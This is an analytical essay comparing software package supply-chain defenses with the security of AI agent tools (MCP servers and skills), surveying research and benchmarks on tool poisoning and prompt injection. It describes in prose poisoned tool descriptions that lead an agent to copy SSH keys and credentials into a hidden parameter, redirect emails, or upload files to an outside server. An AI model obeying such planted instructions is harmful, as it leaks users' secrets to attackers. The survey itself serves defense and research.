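# Agent tools and software packages: where the comparison fails and which defenses carry over

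## How packages and agent tools reach a user

An AI agent is a language model that carries out tasks by calling tools, functions that let it read a file, query a database or send a message. Many of these tools are written by strangers and published in public registries, where anyone can find and install them. The registries closely resemble phone app stores, or npm and PyPI, where programmers get JavaScript and Python packages. Programmers have spent decades developing defenses for software packages. Whether those defenses also protect someone who installs an agent tool depends on how packages and tools each get from their author to the machine where they take effect.

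*Towards Secure Agent Skills* (Li, Wu and colleagues, 2026) compares the three main mechanisms for extending agents so far. ChatGPT Plugins, which OpenAI opened in 2023 and shut down in April 2024, were the most like an app store. Every plugin listed its operations in a typed manifest, ran on its provider's servers and had to pass a review before publication. In November 2024 Anthropic introduced the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open protocol for connecting agents to tools. Until then, connecting M applications to N tools could have required up to M × N separate integrations. Anthropic introduced Agent Skills in October 2025. A skill is a folder of written instructions, often with scripts, that an agent loads when it seems relevant to a task. Li and colleagues argue that each new mechanism became more expressive by dropping constraints. Neither MCP nor the major skill marketplaces require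 a review.

### A package

Take an invented package, temp-convert, that turns Fahrenheit into Celsius. Its developer writes the code, gives it a name and a version number, and uploads the archive to npm. A second developer who wants to use it adds a line to a project file:

```json
"dependencies": { "temp-convert": "^1.2.0" }
```

A program called the resolver reads this line, together with the matching lines of every package that temp-convert itself needs, and picks versions by fixed rules. The caret admits any version from 1.2.0 up to but not including 2.0.0, and npm will normally take the newest one that fits. A persuasive README makes no difference to the resolver. The package manager then writes a lockfile with the exact version, the download address and a hash, a short fingerprint of the archive that changes if a single byte changes. Anyone who later installs from that lockfile gets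 the same bytes or an error. At the end of the route an interpreter runs the code:

```js
export const toCelsius = (f) => (f - 32) * 5 / 9;
```

Each of the classic defenses acts at a particular point on this route. App stores review an app before listing it, while npm and PyPI publish packages immediately and leave review to whoever adopts them. Registries and security companies start scanning new uploads for malicious patterns around the time of publication, either by static analysis (examining the files without running them) or by running them on an isolated machine. The publisher signs the archive when building or uploading it, and an installer can check the signature against the publisher's key. A lockfile pins a project to one exact archive by recording its hash. Permissions apply last, at run time, and phones handle them much better than package managers do. A phone app needs the user's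 permission to use the camera, while an npm package by default gets all the authority of the program that imports it.

Packages are still not safe. *Malicious Agent Skills in the Wild* (Liu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) cites an earlier finding that 74.8% of malicious PyPI packages reached end users. Any comparison of agent tools with packages should use that poor record as its baseline.

### An MCP tool

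An MCP server is a program or service that offers tools, and the application in which the agent runs acts as its client. Under the current specification, Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), the client first sends a request named `tools/list`. The server answers with one entry per tool. For the temperature function an entry could look like this:

```json
{
  "name": "to_celsius",
  "description": "Convert a temperature from Fahrenheit to Celsius.",
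  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": { "fahrenheit": { "type": "number" } },
    "required": ["fahrenheit"]
  }
}
```

The client puts these entries into the model's context, the text the model takes as input. Suppose the user mentions that it is 86 degrees in Austin and asks what that is in Celsius. The model finds a description that fits and produces a call with the tool's name and the argument 86. The client sends the call to the server as a `tools/call` request, and the server runs its function and returns 30. The client adds that result to the context as more text, and the model uses it to write its answer.

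The model decides whether to call a tool mostly from the tool's description, which in a package would be documentation. The specification calls this arrangement "model-controlled". It recommends but does not require (a SHOULD, not a MUST) that a human always be able to deny a call, and the protocol prescribes no particular way of showing calls to the user. The list of tools can also change. A server may notify its clients when that happens, and since the revision that Model Context Protocol (2026) announced in July, list responses include a hint about how long a client may reuse them.

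Some MCP servers are packages and some are not, which matters a great deal for everything that follows. As Google Cloud's *MCP server overview* has it, a local server typically runs on the user's own machine, while a remote server runs on its provider's infrastructure and offers a web address. The user of a local server usually downloads an archive from npm, PyPI or Docker Hub, with a version and a hash. The user of a remote server downloads nothing. A single listing can offer both: Model Context Protocol's *Publishing Remote Servers* has an example in which one email tool comes as an npm package and also as a web address, and the client application picks. (Liu and colleagues contrast skills with MCP on the ground that MCP code runs on separately administered servers. That is true only of the remote kind.)

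The official MCP Registry, still in preview, treats packaged and remote servers differently. It stores metadata that points to packages elsewhere and, according to Model Context Protocol's *The MCP Registry*, leaves security scanning to the package registries and to the marketplaces that build on its data. A remote server without a package has no package registry, so scanning is left to the marketplaces alone. Identity checks also differ. For a Docker image, the registry looks for a label inside the image that matches the server's name, according to Model Context Protocol's *Package Types*. For a remote server, it checks who controls the name but not who controls the address, according to Model Context Protocol's *Remote Servers*. Published entries are immutable, as they are on npm, but an entry that contains a web address fixes only the address, and the operator can replace the program behind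 it at any time.

### A skill

A skill needs just one file, SKILL.md, which opens with a name and a description and continues with instructions in ordinary prose. Here is a harmless one:

```markdown
---
name: weather-note
description: Writes a one-line weather note in Celsius. Use for weather summaries.
---
Convert each temperature with scripts/to_celsius.py.
Give the day's high first, then the low.
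```

Agents load skills in three stages. At startup, the agent loads the name and description of every installed skill, which Agent Skills' *Specification* estimates at about 100 tokens per skill (a token is a word or part of a word). Anthropic puts this text in the system prompt, the standing instructions a model receives before any request. When a skill seems relevant, the agent loads its entire SKILL.md file, which the specification recommends keeping under 5,000 tokens. It loads scripts and reference files only if the instructions in that file call for them.

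Li and colleagues write the middle step as a function r(q, mᵢ), which equals 1 if the skill with name and description mᵢ applies to the request q, and 0 if it does not. The model computes r by judging the meaning of a description that the skill's author wrote, so the function resembles a resolver's rule only in its notation. In the last step, when the agent runs a script, only the output enters the context, so the model uses the result without seeing the source code that produced it.

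In Li and colleagues' analysis, a user who installs a skill approves roughly the actions that the skill declares, but in effect grants it every action open to the agent, such as file access and network calls, for all later sessions. A sandbox can limit those actions, but the skill format does not require one. The format has an optional `allowed-tools` field, marked as experimental in the specification, where a skill's author can list tools for pre-approval. Li and colleagues report that Claude Code applies this field but Anthropic's Agent SDK does not read it, so a user who relies on it has to know which of the two is running the skill.

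### Prompt injection and the confused deputy

Prompt injection is text from an outside party that a model obeys as if its user or developer had written it. For example, an agent asked to summarize a web page might recommend a certain shop because a sentence on the page tells any AI reader to do so. Databases had a related problem, which parameterized queries prevent by sending the query and the user's values separately, so that the database never treats a value as part of a command. Li and colleagues point out that skills lack this separation, because the skill author's instructions and the data the skill picks up at run time reach the model as the same kind of text. They think MCP keeps part of the boundary because the model calls typed operations with defined parameters. A filter that looks for instructions where only data should be can't easily spot an injection in a skill file, which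 is itself made up of instructions. People call prompt injection "tool poisoning" when the injected text is in a tool's description or other metadata.

A confused deputy is a program tricked into using its privileges for someone who lacks them. In the textbook case, a compiler on a shared computer had permission to write to a directory that also held the billing records. A user without that permission told the compiler to save its debugging output to the billing file, and the compiler overwrote the records. The access check passed because the compiler was allowed to write there. An agent with access to a user's mailbox, files and cloud credentials is in the same position, and prompt injection is one way to confuse it. The operating system can check whether the agent may open a file, but not whether the user wanted it opened or a stranger's tool description led the agent to open it.

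### How many skills there are

Nobody has an authoritative count of agent skills. In January 2026, Liu and colleagues found that no agent vendor kept an official central registry of all deployed skills, though there are several community indexes. *From Instructions to Exploits* (Zhao, Wang and colleagues, 2026) gives the latest figures, from October 2026: 67,453 skills on ClawHub (the registry of the OpenClaw agent), over 963,000 on skills.sh and more than 2.27 million on SkillsMP. Earlier figures appear in Liu and colleagues' study, in Saha, Faghih and Feizi's *Under the Hood of SKILL.md* (2026) and in *Skills Are Not Islands* (2026).

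| Registry | Liu and colleagues, January 2026 | Saha and colleagues, May 2026 | *Skills Are Not Islands*, June 2026 | Zhao and colleagues, October 2026 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| ClawHub | | 64,000 | | 67,453 |
| skills.sh | | 91,000 | | over 963,000 |
| SkillsMP | 73,193 | | 1,640,440 | over 2.27 million |
| LobeHub | | 288,000 | | |
| SkillsDirectory | | 36,000 | | |
| skills.rest | 25,187 | | | |

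Zhao and colleagues think the totals differ because the sites collect and aggregate skills differently, and the differences in what each site counts support this explanation. ClawHub's total is the number of latest public versions in a snapshot that the registry released. SkillsMP indexes public skill files on GitHub, regardless of who uploaded them or why. Vercel's *Introducing skills, the open agent skills ecosystem* describes skills.sh as a directory and leaderboard for use with the company's command-line installer. The skills.sh total rose tenfold between May and October, while ClawHub's barely changed. A change in what skills.sh counts could explain its rise just as well as real growth could.

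Many of the skill files on GitHub are copies. *GitSkills* (Destefanis, Graziotin and colleagues, 2026) collected 3,797,117 SKILL.md files from 282,200 public GitHub repositories in July 2026 and found 1,877,981 distinct contents, about half the total. Developers reuse a skill by copying its folder into another repository, so one popular skill can appear many times. By contrast, *Skills Are Not Islands* found that only 0.52% of its SkillsMP records were identical by hash. SkillsMP may drop most copies before listing them, or the two studies may have hashed different things.

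Dead entries and filtering also affect the totals. About one in eight of the skills that SkillsMP listed in June could not be downloaded, mostly because links were dead or repositories had gone private or lost the file. *How Agent Skills Evolve* (2026) found 296,051 candidate files in repositories with some minimal visibility and recent activity, and had 84,200 skills left after filtering and deduplication. Any claim that some percentage of skills is malicious therefore needs to state the total it is based on, because plausible totals range from tens of thousands to millions.

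### Where the two paths diverge

When an interpreter runs a package's code, it skips the comments. A language model reads tool descriptions and SKILL.md files, and any sentence in them may affect what the model does next, which is why Saha and colleagues call SKILL.md "operational text". A skill's scripts and a local server's code still run on an ordinary interpreter, so the comparison with packages holds up well for those parts.

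Agent tools also change what a defender can check in advance. A package's archive contains the instructions that the machine will carry out, unless it fetches more at run time, although the code can be hard to analyze and malicious packages do get past scanners. With a remote server, there is no archive to inspect. With a skill, the defender has every file but can't determine the effect from the files alone, because it depends on the model, the user's request and whatever else is in the context. Li and colleagues add that a one-line description is too vague to test the instructions against. A signature can show that the file is the one its author published, but it doesn't solve any of these problems.

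Packages and agent tools also differ in who chooses them. A developer names a package and the resolver applies its rules. A person may install a skill or connect a server, but the model then decides which tool to use for each request. Some registries also let agents search for and install tools directly, so search ranking can affect the choice. *GitSkills* describes the model's selection as probabilistic, with no compiler or type checker to verify it. Developers who install from the same lockfile get the same code, but users with the same skills installed may trigger different ones by wording the same request differently.

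## Three views of how to secure agent tools

Specialists disagree about how much these differences should change the defenses. Some treat agent tools as software dependencies and would secure them as they secure packages (the dependency view). Others hold that a tool's text is part of the program, so any check that ignores its meaning is incomplete (the semantic view). A third group expects text to keep misleading models whatever anyone checks, and would limit what the agent can do (the containment view).

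### Tools as dependencies

*The sorry state of skill distribution*, by the security company Trail of Bits, describes the skill as "a new style of dependency", with marketplaces that run alongside the existing package managers. Trail of Bits recommends finding out where each dependency comes from, pinning it to one version, and limiting who may add or update it. This advice would apply equally to npm packages. An organization can follow it by keeping its own small marketplace of reviewed skills. Trail of Bits publishes a curated collection for this purpose, and it strongly discourages using ClawHub and skills.sh for agents that work in sensitive settings.

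This approach is attractive because nobody has to build a system that recognizes malicious prose. It excludes a skill by an unknown author, however innocent the skill looks, because nobody has vouched for it.

In *Formal Analysis and Supply Chain Security for Agentic AI Skills*, Bhardwaj (2026) argues that skill registries have the same weaknesses as npm and PyPI, but with higher stakes because skills run with broad privileges alongside a powerful model. His tool, SkillFortify, adapts several package defenses to skills. It records a hash for each skill in a lockfile and produces a bill of materials, an inventory of everything the agent depends on, in a format that companies' existing vulnerability software can read. It also grades skills on four levels, from unsigned to formally verified, modeled on SLSA (Supply-chain Levels for Software Artifacts), a framework that grades the evidence for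 how and from what source software was built. A company could then refuse any skill below a chosen level.

*Ring-0 by Default* (2026), which compares agents with operating systems, treats skills and MCP servers as the agent's packages and finds four of seven standard packaging mechanisms missing. Old attacks such as typosquatting, dependency confusion and rug pulls therefore remain possible. In typosquatting, an attacker publishes a package under a name one typo away from a popular one. In dependency confusion, the attacker gives a public package the same name as a company's private one, so that the installer fetches the wrong one. If this diagnosis is right, much of the trouble with agent tools is unfinished engineering, and it would be strange to invent new defenses before putting the known ones in place.

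### Text as part of the program

Research on malicious packages has generally assumed that the payload is in executable code. Zhao and colleagues think this assumption fails for skills, and give the example of a skill for editing PowerPoint files. Its instructions tell the agent to save the edited presentation and then always run a backup script on it, which sends the file to an outside server. The skill comes from a GitHub repository named promptinject-agent-skills, so it may be a researcher's example rather than something an attacker published.

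A reviewer who reads only the instructions sees a routine backup step, and one who reads only the script sees an upload. A rule against all uploads would also flag the many honest skills that perform them. A reviewer has to read the instructions and script together to see that a possibly confidential file leaves the machine although the user asked only for an edit. Zhao and colleagues conclude that a scanner has to analyze instructions and code as one program.

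Badhe and Tiwari (2026), in *Agent Skill Security*, make the same criticism of provenance tools. They accept that bills of materials, SLSA and Sigstore (a service for signing software) are highly effective at protecting the distribution of code, but call them "fundamentally blind to the semantic layer", meaning everything that depends on how a model interprets a skill's text. They divide attacks on a registry into structural and semantic ones. A missing signature, an altered file and a rollback to an older, vulnerable version are structural faults, which fixed rules can catch. But a skill that is correctly signed, unaltered and up to date can still have a description that doesn't match its instructions, request more permissions than its job requires, or contain a hidden prompt injection. Catching these problems requires comparing the skill's stated purpose with what its instructions would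 make an agent do, and Badhe and Tiwari consider a language model necessary for that comparison.

Users are badly placed to compare a skill's label with its instructions. ramimac.me's *Spooky Skills* calls agent skills "the hardest form of supply chain artifact" and points out that a person sees the label while the agent receives the instructions, which can do something completely different. The description also influences which skill the model selects, so a dishonest description can affect that choice before any script runs.

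### A model that anyone can mislead

*Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published by the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) in December 2025, is the clearest short statement of the containment view. Its author, David C, the NCSC's technical director for platforms research, calls a language model an "inherently confusable deputy" because it has no built-in boundary between data and instructions. Developers can repair an ordinary confused deputy, such as the compiler that overwrote the billing records, but he doubts that anyone can repair this one. He thinks developers can only make attacks rarer and less damaging.

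He therefore wants designers to start by assuming the worst case, in which an attacker has direct access to every tool the agent can call. The main protection should come from deterministic safeguards, ordinary program code that blocks certain actions whatever the model outputs. He also likes a rule, from an exchange on X between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista, that a model processing text from some party should have its privileges reduced to that party's. An agent reading email from strangers would then have only tools that its owner would give a stranger. If the remaining risk is too high, he says, the system may not be a good use for a language model.

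The design work he cites includes *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, by Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025). Their principle is that once an agent has taken in untrusted input, that input must not be able to trigger any action with harmful side effects. They think general-purpose agents built on the current class of language models are unlikely to offer reliable guarantees, so they propose six designs that deliberately give up some generality.

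In one design, plan-then-execute, the agent commits to a list of tool calls before it sees any outside data. If the user asks it to send today's schedule to the boss, the plan is to read the calendar and then send an email to the boss's address. A malicious calendar entry can still corrupt the text of the email, but it can't add a third step. In another design, one model has tools but never reads untrusted text, and a second model reads that text but has no tools. Ordinary software stores what the second model extracts, such as an email address, under a placeholder name. The first model can pass the placeholder to a tool without seeing its contents.

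These limits hold even when nobody recognizes the attack. David C warns against filtering for known bad phrases because an attacker can reword an injection in endless ways. However it is worded, an injection can't add a step to a fixed plan.

Both works deal with outside data that an agent reads while working. A skill is harder to secure because the user installs it so that the agent will follow its author's instructions. Under the rule about privileges, an agent using a stranger's skill would have only a stranger's privileges, and many useful skills would stop working. The user could grant more privileges to authors who deserve them, but would then need to know who the author is, which is the main issue in the dependency view.

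### Common ground

Trail of Bits gives the dependency camp's advice, but largely for the semantic camp's reasons. It got malicious test skills past every scanner it tried and concluded that no amount of scanning or model-based analysis can reliably detect malicious content in skills. It argues that skills mix code, data and natural language freely, and that an instruction that is harmless in one environment can be harmful in another. It therefore relies on people to decide whom to trust.

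The other views also borrow from each other. Bhardwaj concedes that his formal guarantees don't cover a skill whose description manipulates the model into unintended actions. Badhe and Tiwari keep signature checks, add least privilege at run time (each skill gets only the access its task requires), and say that no single defense is enough. David C recommends marking outside text as data, which makes injection harder, and logging failed tool calls, which may reveal an attacker who is still experimenting. They disagree mostly about which defense to rely on when another fails.

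One registry can have all three problems at once. *Carried-Over and Agent-Native Threats in the Supply Chain of LLM Agent Skills* (Li, Guo and colleagues, 2026) examined all 48,682 skills then on ClawHub for honest mistakes. Among the skills whose dependencies could be resolved, 49.6% relied on a package version with a publicly listed vulnerability, a familiar failure of package hygiene. Risky installation commands, such as downloading a script and immediately running it, were at least 6.6 times as common in SKILL.md files as in the skills' installer scripts, where a conventional scan would look. The study also tested a live agent with 200 skills flagged by its screening, planting a command in the outside content the agent processed. The agent executed the command with 48.5% of these skills, almost always in its own command shell before the skill had started. The command reached a flaw in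 the skill itself in only 5.0%, so repairing the skills would have prevented few of these attacks. The study leaves out deliberately malicious skills, which could be distributed quite differently.

### Five questions on which they part

1. Does text differ from code in kind? David C thinks so, and expects that nothing will do for prompts what parameterized queries did for databases. Zhao and colleagues are more optimistic. They translate a skill's instructions into a program-like form before analyzing them, which can only work if harmful text mostly reduces to a limited set of operations, such as reading a file and sending it somewhere. Evidence that it does would favor the semantic view. If attackers can keep producing the same harm in words that no analysis connects with it, containment looks better. A reliable way to make models ignore commands in tool descriptions would help the dependency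 view, because a description would then be nearly as inert as a README.

2. Do real attackers exploit the difference? If the malicious tools in public registries mostly deliver ordinary malware, package defenses address most of the present harm. The semantic view gains if text often does the damage without any malicious code. Frequent attacks through honest tools, in which outside content hijacks the agent, would favor containment. Any such count needs some caution, since researchers can count only what their methods detect, and attackers have little reason to bother with subtle prose while crude malware still works.

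3. Can anyone judge meaning before installation? The semantic view needs a checker that misses few malicious tools and rarely flags harmless ones. On a registry the size of ClawHub, a false positive rate of just 1% would mean roughly 670 false alarms. The checker also has to withstand attackers who can run it on their own skill and revise until it passes, so a high score on a fixed set of samples proves rather little. If checkers fail against such attackers, the case for human curation and for hard limits on the agent becomes stronger.

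4. What does a signature still buy? In Bhardwaj's scheme, the level for signed skills gives assurance about the author's identity and none about the skill's behavior. Even that would be valuable if most harmful tools come from throwaway accounts, tampering or silent updates, because an identity requirement together with pinning would stop many of them. It would be worth much less if the harm comes from reputable publishers whose accounts someone has hijacked, or from remote servers, which leave the user no file to verify. Those findings would favor the other two views.

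5. Can the user fix the agent's choices in advance? A lockfile can't do it, since the model still picks among the installed skills. Plan-then-execute settles the sequence of calls before outside data arrives, but the model reads the tool descriptions before it writes the plan, so a poisoned description could still shape it. If agents can do most of their useful work with a short list of approved tools, the dependency view gains, since people can review a short list. If they lose little by working from fixed plans, containment gains. But if a useful agent has to search open registries in the middle of a task, nobody can review its tools beforehand, and some automatic check of their text becomes hard to avoid.

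## Text that a model reads compared with code that a machine runs

### An adding tool with a hidden request

The security company Invariant Labs introduced the term "tool poisoning" in its *MCP Security Notification*, published on April 1, 2025, with two demonstrations. The first used an MCP server that offered a tool for adding two numbers. The tool's code correctly returned the sum. But the tool also had a text parameter called `sidenote`, and its description contained instructions for the model to fill this field with the contents of two files from the user's machine. One was a configuration file of the coding agent Cursor, which often holds the credentials for the user's other MCP servers. The other was the user's private SSH key, which can give access to remote machines. The description also included the pretext that the tool would not work otherwise, and instructions to explain the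 mathematics of addition at length without mentioning the files.

Invariant Labs connected the server to Cursor and ran the tool. The model read both files, copied their contents into the side note and made the call. This delivered the contents to the attacker, because a client sends a tool's arguments to the server that runs it. Cursor asked the user to confirm the call, but its dialog showed a short summary with the tool's name, and even the expanded view left out the key.

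A programmer who reviewed the function would find an addition and an unused parameter. The attacker didn't need a bug in the file system either, since the agent had permission to read the files. The agent is again a confused deputy, misled by a few sentences of English. Invariant Labs gives no success rate, so the demonstration shows that the attack can work but not how often.

### How an uncalled tool affects another one

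For the second demonstration, Invariant Labs connected Cursor to a trusted server with a tool for sending email and a malicious server with another adding tool. According to the adding tool's description, the email tool had to send every message to one address whenever the adding tool was present, supposedly to prevent a technical fault. When the user asked the agent to email somebody else, it sent the message to the attacker's address. Nobody had asked for a sum, and the model did not need to call the adding tool. The log showed an ordinary call to a trusted tool, with only the recipient argument wrong.

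The notation of Birhan, Rostamzadeh and colleagues (2026), in *COPEX*, a benchmark of attacks on MCP agents, makes the reason easy to see. At each turn t, the model M picks its next action a from a probability distribution:

aₜ ~ M( · | h, p, Sₜ, Rₜ )

Here h is the system's standing instruction, p is the user's request, Sₜ is the set of descriptions and parameter lists of all the tools available at that turn, and Rₜ is everything that tools have returned so far. The distribution depends on all of Sₜ, including the entries for tools that the model is not about to call. When the model fills in the recipient of an email, its input includes the adding tool's description as well as the email tool's, so a poisoned tool can affect the email just by being on the list.

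Packages can interfere with each other too. In JavaScript, an imported package can overwrite a built-in function that every other package in the program uses. But the package has to run to do this, and afterwards a debugger can find the overwritten function in memory. The poisoned description did not change the email tool's code or description. Someone who approves tools one at a time can easily miss such an attack, because a sentence about an email tool has no effect until the user connects one.

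### Why a database can keep commands apart from data

Parameterized queries keep a user's values separate from the database's commands. If a website visitor types part of a command where a customer's name should go, the database looks for a customer with that name, so the defense works even if nobody recognizes the input as malicious.

David C argues that language models lack such a barrier because of how they work. In his example, a recruiter asks a model to score job applications, and one candidate's CV contains a hidden instruction to approve it for interview. The developer thinks of the CV as data, but the model receives the recruiter's request and the candidate's instruction as text in a single sequence of tokens, and predicts the next token. Developers can mark the CV as outside material, and companies can train models to prioritize the developer's instructions. David C sees these measures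 as attempts to impose a distinction between instructions and data on a technology that has none.

This is a good argument against expecting a guarantee, but much weaker evidence of how often a given model will be fooled. People also read orders and information with the same eyes, and most don't obey a stranger's letter just because it contains an imperative. A model could learn to ignore such instructions almost all the time without a separate channel for data. Whether that is good enough depends on what the agent can do and how many times an attacker can try.

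### Instructions that an agent is supposed to follow

With emails and web pages, a developer can aim for a simple rule that the model never obeys instructions found in outside content. The rule fits tool descriptions badly, because a description may legitimately tell the model to write dates in a certain format or to call a login tool first. It doesn't fit skills at all, because users install them for their instructions.

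In *Skill-Inject*, Schmotz, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues (2026) argue that skill files pose a problem for two defenses, marking outside text with special delimiters and training a model not to carry out instructions in a section reserved for data. Both defenses treat an instruction as suspicious if it appears where instructions don't belong. Since a skill file is meant to contain instructions, the defender has to find out whether some of them are bad. They see the same problem for designs that fix an agent's actions in advance from the user's request, because people install skills to supply steps that the request leaves out.

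A defender also can't always tell from an instruction alone whether it is harmful. Schmotz and colleagues give the example of a skill that tells the agent to share a summary with the team through a collaboration service, which is ordinary when the agent is editing internal documentation but a leak when the files contain credentials. They also use an instruction to back up every edited presentation to an outside server, much like the PowerPoint skill that Zhao and colleagues describe. An agent that follows this instruction is doing its job if the company has approved the server, but the same skill file makes it leak a document if the company forbids such transfers.

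Code shares this last difficulty. A Python script that uploads files can be backing them up or stealing them, depending on who owns the server and whether the user agreed. Help desks and intruders can use the same remote-control software. For both code and text, whether an action is harmful depends on permission, which is seldom recorded in the file. Any difference in kind between code and text must lie in how well anyone can predict the action itself.

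### Three objections from the side of code

A skeptic could cite Rice's theorem to argue that nobody can reliably tell whether a program is harmful either. The theorem, which Henry Gordon Rice published in 1953, concerns what programs do, as opposed to how their code is written. If some programs have a behavioral property and others lack it, no algorithm can decide correctly, for every program, whether it has that property.

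No algorithm can correctly decide, for every program, whether it steals the user's keys. For any program P that only calculates, someone can write a second program that runs P and then uploads the keys. The second program steals the keys exactly when P finishes, so a perfect detector of key theft could also tell whether any such P finishes. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no algorithm can do that in general.

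The theorem refutes the claim that code, unlike text, can be checked perfectly. But it only rules out a checker that is right about every program. A checker may still be right about most programs, or reject any it cannot verify, and a registry could accept only code simple enough to analyze.

The theorem is less of an obstacle for the model itself. A model with fixed weights and a limit on the length of its output always finishes, so anyone who has a copy can find out what it does in a given context by running it. The theorem applies again if an agent can launch arbitrary programs. Even for the model alone, there are too many contexts to test them all. With a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens, a request of only 20 tokens can take 10¹⁰⁰ forms. Most of these are gibberish, but the sensible ones are still far too numerous to try.

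The skeptic's second objection is that attackers can hide what code does. They can scramble a program until no person can read it, make it wait for a certain date, or have it download the harmful part later. This is true, and it weakens any argument that prose is more opaque than code. Invariant Labs' poisoned description would have alarmed anyone who saw it, and the attack worked partly because Cursor didn't show it. A human reviewer would probably catch that description sooner than a theft buried in a few thousand lines of compressed JavaScript.

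Third, packages, like tools, can do harm before anyone uses them. An npm package can declare a script that runs during installation, before any program has imported the package, and attackers have long exploited this. A user can tell npm to ignore installation scripts, and many packages will work without them. A model, however, needs some text about each tool to choose sensibly among them. The client could replace the author's description with its own, but somebody would have to write it.

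### What a specification adds

All three objections have some force, but none of them shows that text has a specified meaning, as code does. Anyone who knows the rules of JavaScript can see that the temperature function described earlier will never open a file, whatever number it receives. That conclusion requires no testing, and it holds for any interpreter that follows the rules.

Nobody can reason this way about a sentence such as "always back up the file", because no standard specifies what a model must do in response. One model may upload the file, another may ask the user first, and a third may refuse. The outcome can also change with the descriptions of the other tools, the company's policy or a new version of the model. A tester can try a few hundred contexts and report what happened, but those results don't guarantee how the model will behave in the next one.

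Incidents are also easier to repeat with code. If a suspicious program misbehaves on a test machine, an analyst can restore the machine and run the program again. With the same clock, network responses and other inputs, the program will usually do the same thing. An incident involving a model is harder to repeat when the model runs on a provider's servers, where the provider may replace it. Randomness is a smaller problem. Birhan and colleagues reduced it by setting the temperature of their models to 0, which makes a model favor its most likely token at every step. Even a perfectly repeatable run shows only what the model does in that context.

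Text that a model reads and code that a machine runs differ in kind only in what someone can prove about them before using them. Most people who install an npm package prove nothing about it, so for them the practical difference is one of degree.

### One poisoned text, many readers

If the effect of a text depends on its reader, the same poisoned description should work on some models and fail on others. In *MCPTox* (August 2025), Wang, Gao and colleagues tested this with 353 genuine tools from 45 real MCP servers. They used language models to write poisoned tools, checked them by hand, and ended up with 1,348 test cases (though their breakdown by attack type adds up to 1,497). In each test, the model received the server's genuine tools and one poisoned tool, then a harmless request. An attack counted as successful only if the model used a genuine tool to do the harm. The poisoned tool never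 ran, as in Invariant Labs' second demonstration.

Across 20 model settings, the average attack success rate was 36.5%, ranging from 5.1% for Qwen3-14b without reasoning to 72.8% for OpenAI's o1-mini. Attacks that altered one detail of an action the user had requested, such as the recipient of an email, succeeded most often, at 46.7%. Models almost never refused, and the highest refusal rate, from Claude 3.7 Sonnet, was under 3%. When attacks failed, the model had usually ignored the poisoned text.

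Wang and colleagues tested the Qwen models with reasoning mode on and off, keeping the weights and the poisoned descriptions the same. Turning reasoning on raised the attack's success rate from 5.1% to 27.1% for the 14-billion-parameter model and from 23.7% to 58.5% for the 32-billion-parameter one. Wang and colleagues took this as a sign that more capable models are often more vulnerable because they follow instructions better.

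Whether a malicious instruction works also depends on where it appears. Wang and colleagues moved malicious instructions from tool results, where the older benchmark InjecAgent puts them, into tool descriptions. With Qwen3-8b in reasoning mode, these succeeded 0.1% of the time, compared with 41.8% for instructions written for descriptions. Wang and colleagues suspect that the older instructions failed because they didn't say when to act. An instruction in a description is one line among many, rather than the latest thing the model has read, as it would be in a tool's result.

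### The same test for skills

Schmotz and colleagues published their benchmark in February 2026. They inserted harmful instructions into 23 skills and combined them with realistic tasks, which gave 202 pairs. Some instructions were plainly destructive, such as one to delete all the user's files. Others, like the backup instruction, could be legitimate, and for these the researchers could add a company policy that allowed or forbade the action. They ran models from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google, each in its own company's coding agent. A separate model judged from the commands and files whether the agent had finished the user's task and whether it had carried out the attack.

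Without any policy, agents carried out between 8.6% (Claude Haiku 4.5) and 67.6% (Gemini 3 Flash) of the ambiguous instructions. These figures are from the paper's full results table; its text gives 41% to 79% for the same condition, without explaining the difference. Some of Haiku's apparent resistance may just be a failure to follow the skill, since it finished only 64.8% of the users' tasks, while Claude Opus 4.5 finished 96.1%.

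A policy that forbade the action helped some models far more than others. The attack success rate fell from 30.2% to 6.5% for GPT-5.2 and from 26.6% to 7.2% for Opus 4.5, but only from 67.6% to 56.8% for Gemini 3 Flash. When the policy expressly allowed the action, so that obeying was correct, Opus still carried it out in only 1.4% of cases. In one of these runs, it described the policy as malicious text made to look official. A model that resists malicious instructions can therefore also refuse legitimate ones, and a low attack success rate doesn't distinguish correct refusals from mistaken ones.

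Placing the same harmful instruction on different lines of the skill file made a considerable difference, but using four different versions of the user's task made no statistically significant difference. This is evidence against the idea that the user's request always matters, at least for attacks that don't depend on a particular request.

When Schmotz and colleagues moved the harmful part of a skill from its text into a script and had the skill tell the agent to run it, the attack success rate rose from 53.8% to 71.8% for ambiguous actions and from 53.7% to 62.8% for obviously harmful ones. This is evidence against the view that text is the greater danger. The model often ran the script without reading it. A model sometimes refuses a harmful instruction that it reads, but an interpreter runs whatever code it receives. The skill's text still mattered because it got the script running, but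 the payload was ordinary code that a conventional scanner could have examined.

### Newer models

*MCP Tool Poisoning in Agentic AI Frameworks* (Shaikh and Montaruli, 2026), a paper for a November 2026 workshop, reports the widest test of tool poisoning so far. The researchers combined 18 models with 12 agent frameworks (the software that connects a model to its tools) and 45 attacks, and let the tools actually run. They found that 22.9% of the attacks succeeded. In 12.1% of those successes, they confirmed that a secret had reached their server. In most of the others, the evidence was that the agent had called the attacker's tool.

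Attack success rates varied widely by model, from 0.4% for Claude Fable 5 to 49.7% for Amazon's Nova Pro. The choice of framework usually made little difference. Nine of the twelve frameworks had success rates between 23% and 26%, and none of the twelve contained a deliberate defense against poisoned descriptions. Attacks on Claude Opus 4.8 succeeded 8 times out of 530, and the model refused 223 times with an explicit reference to the poisoned description, whereas Wang and colleagues had observed silence a year earlier. This result is also evidence against a general rule that more capable models are easier to poison. Claude Sonnet 5 sometimes identified the text as a prompt injection and then followed it anyway.

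Rates were much higher in two other recent tests. Birhan and colleagues tested nine models in an otherwise identical agent setup. The models' average rates ranged from 44.3% for Claude Opus 4.7 to 81.6% for Grok 4.3, but these include attacks that the model can't see, such as one that redirects the network connection and succeeded with every model. *AutoRedClaw* (2026) measures whether an attacker can establish lasting poisoning through the files that agents rely on, including skills. The table gives the range in each test, using only the attacks through servers and tools from Birhan and colleagues and only the results for skills in the OpenClaw agent from *AutoRedClaw*.

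| Test | Attack | Lowest success rate | Highest success rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Wang and colleagues, August 2025 | poisoned tool descriptions | 5.1% (Qwen3-14b, reasoning off) | 72.8% (o1-mini) |
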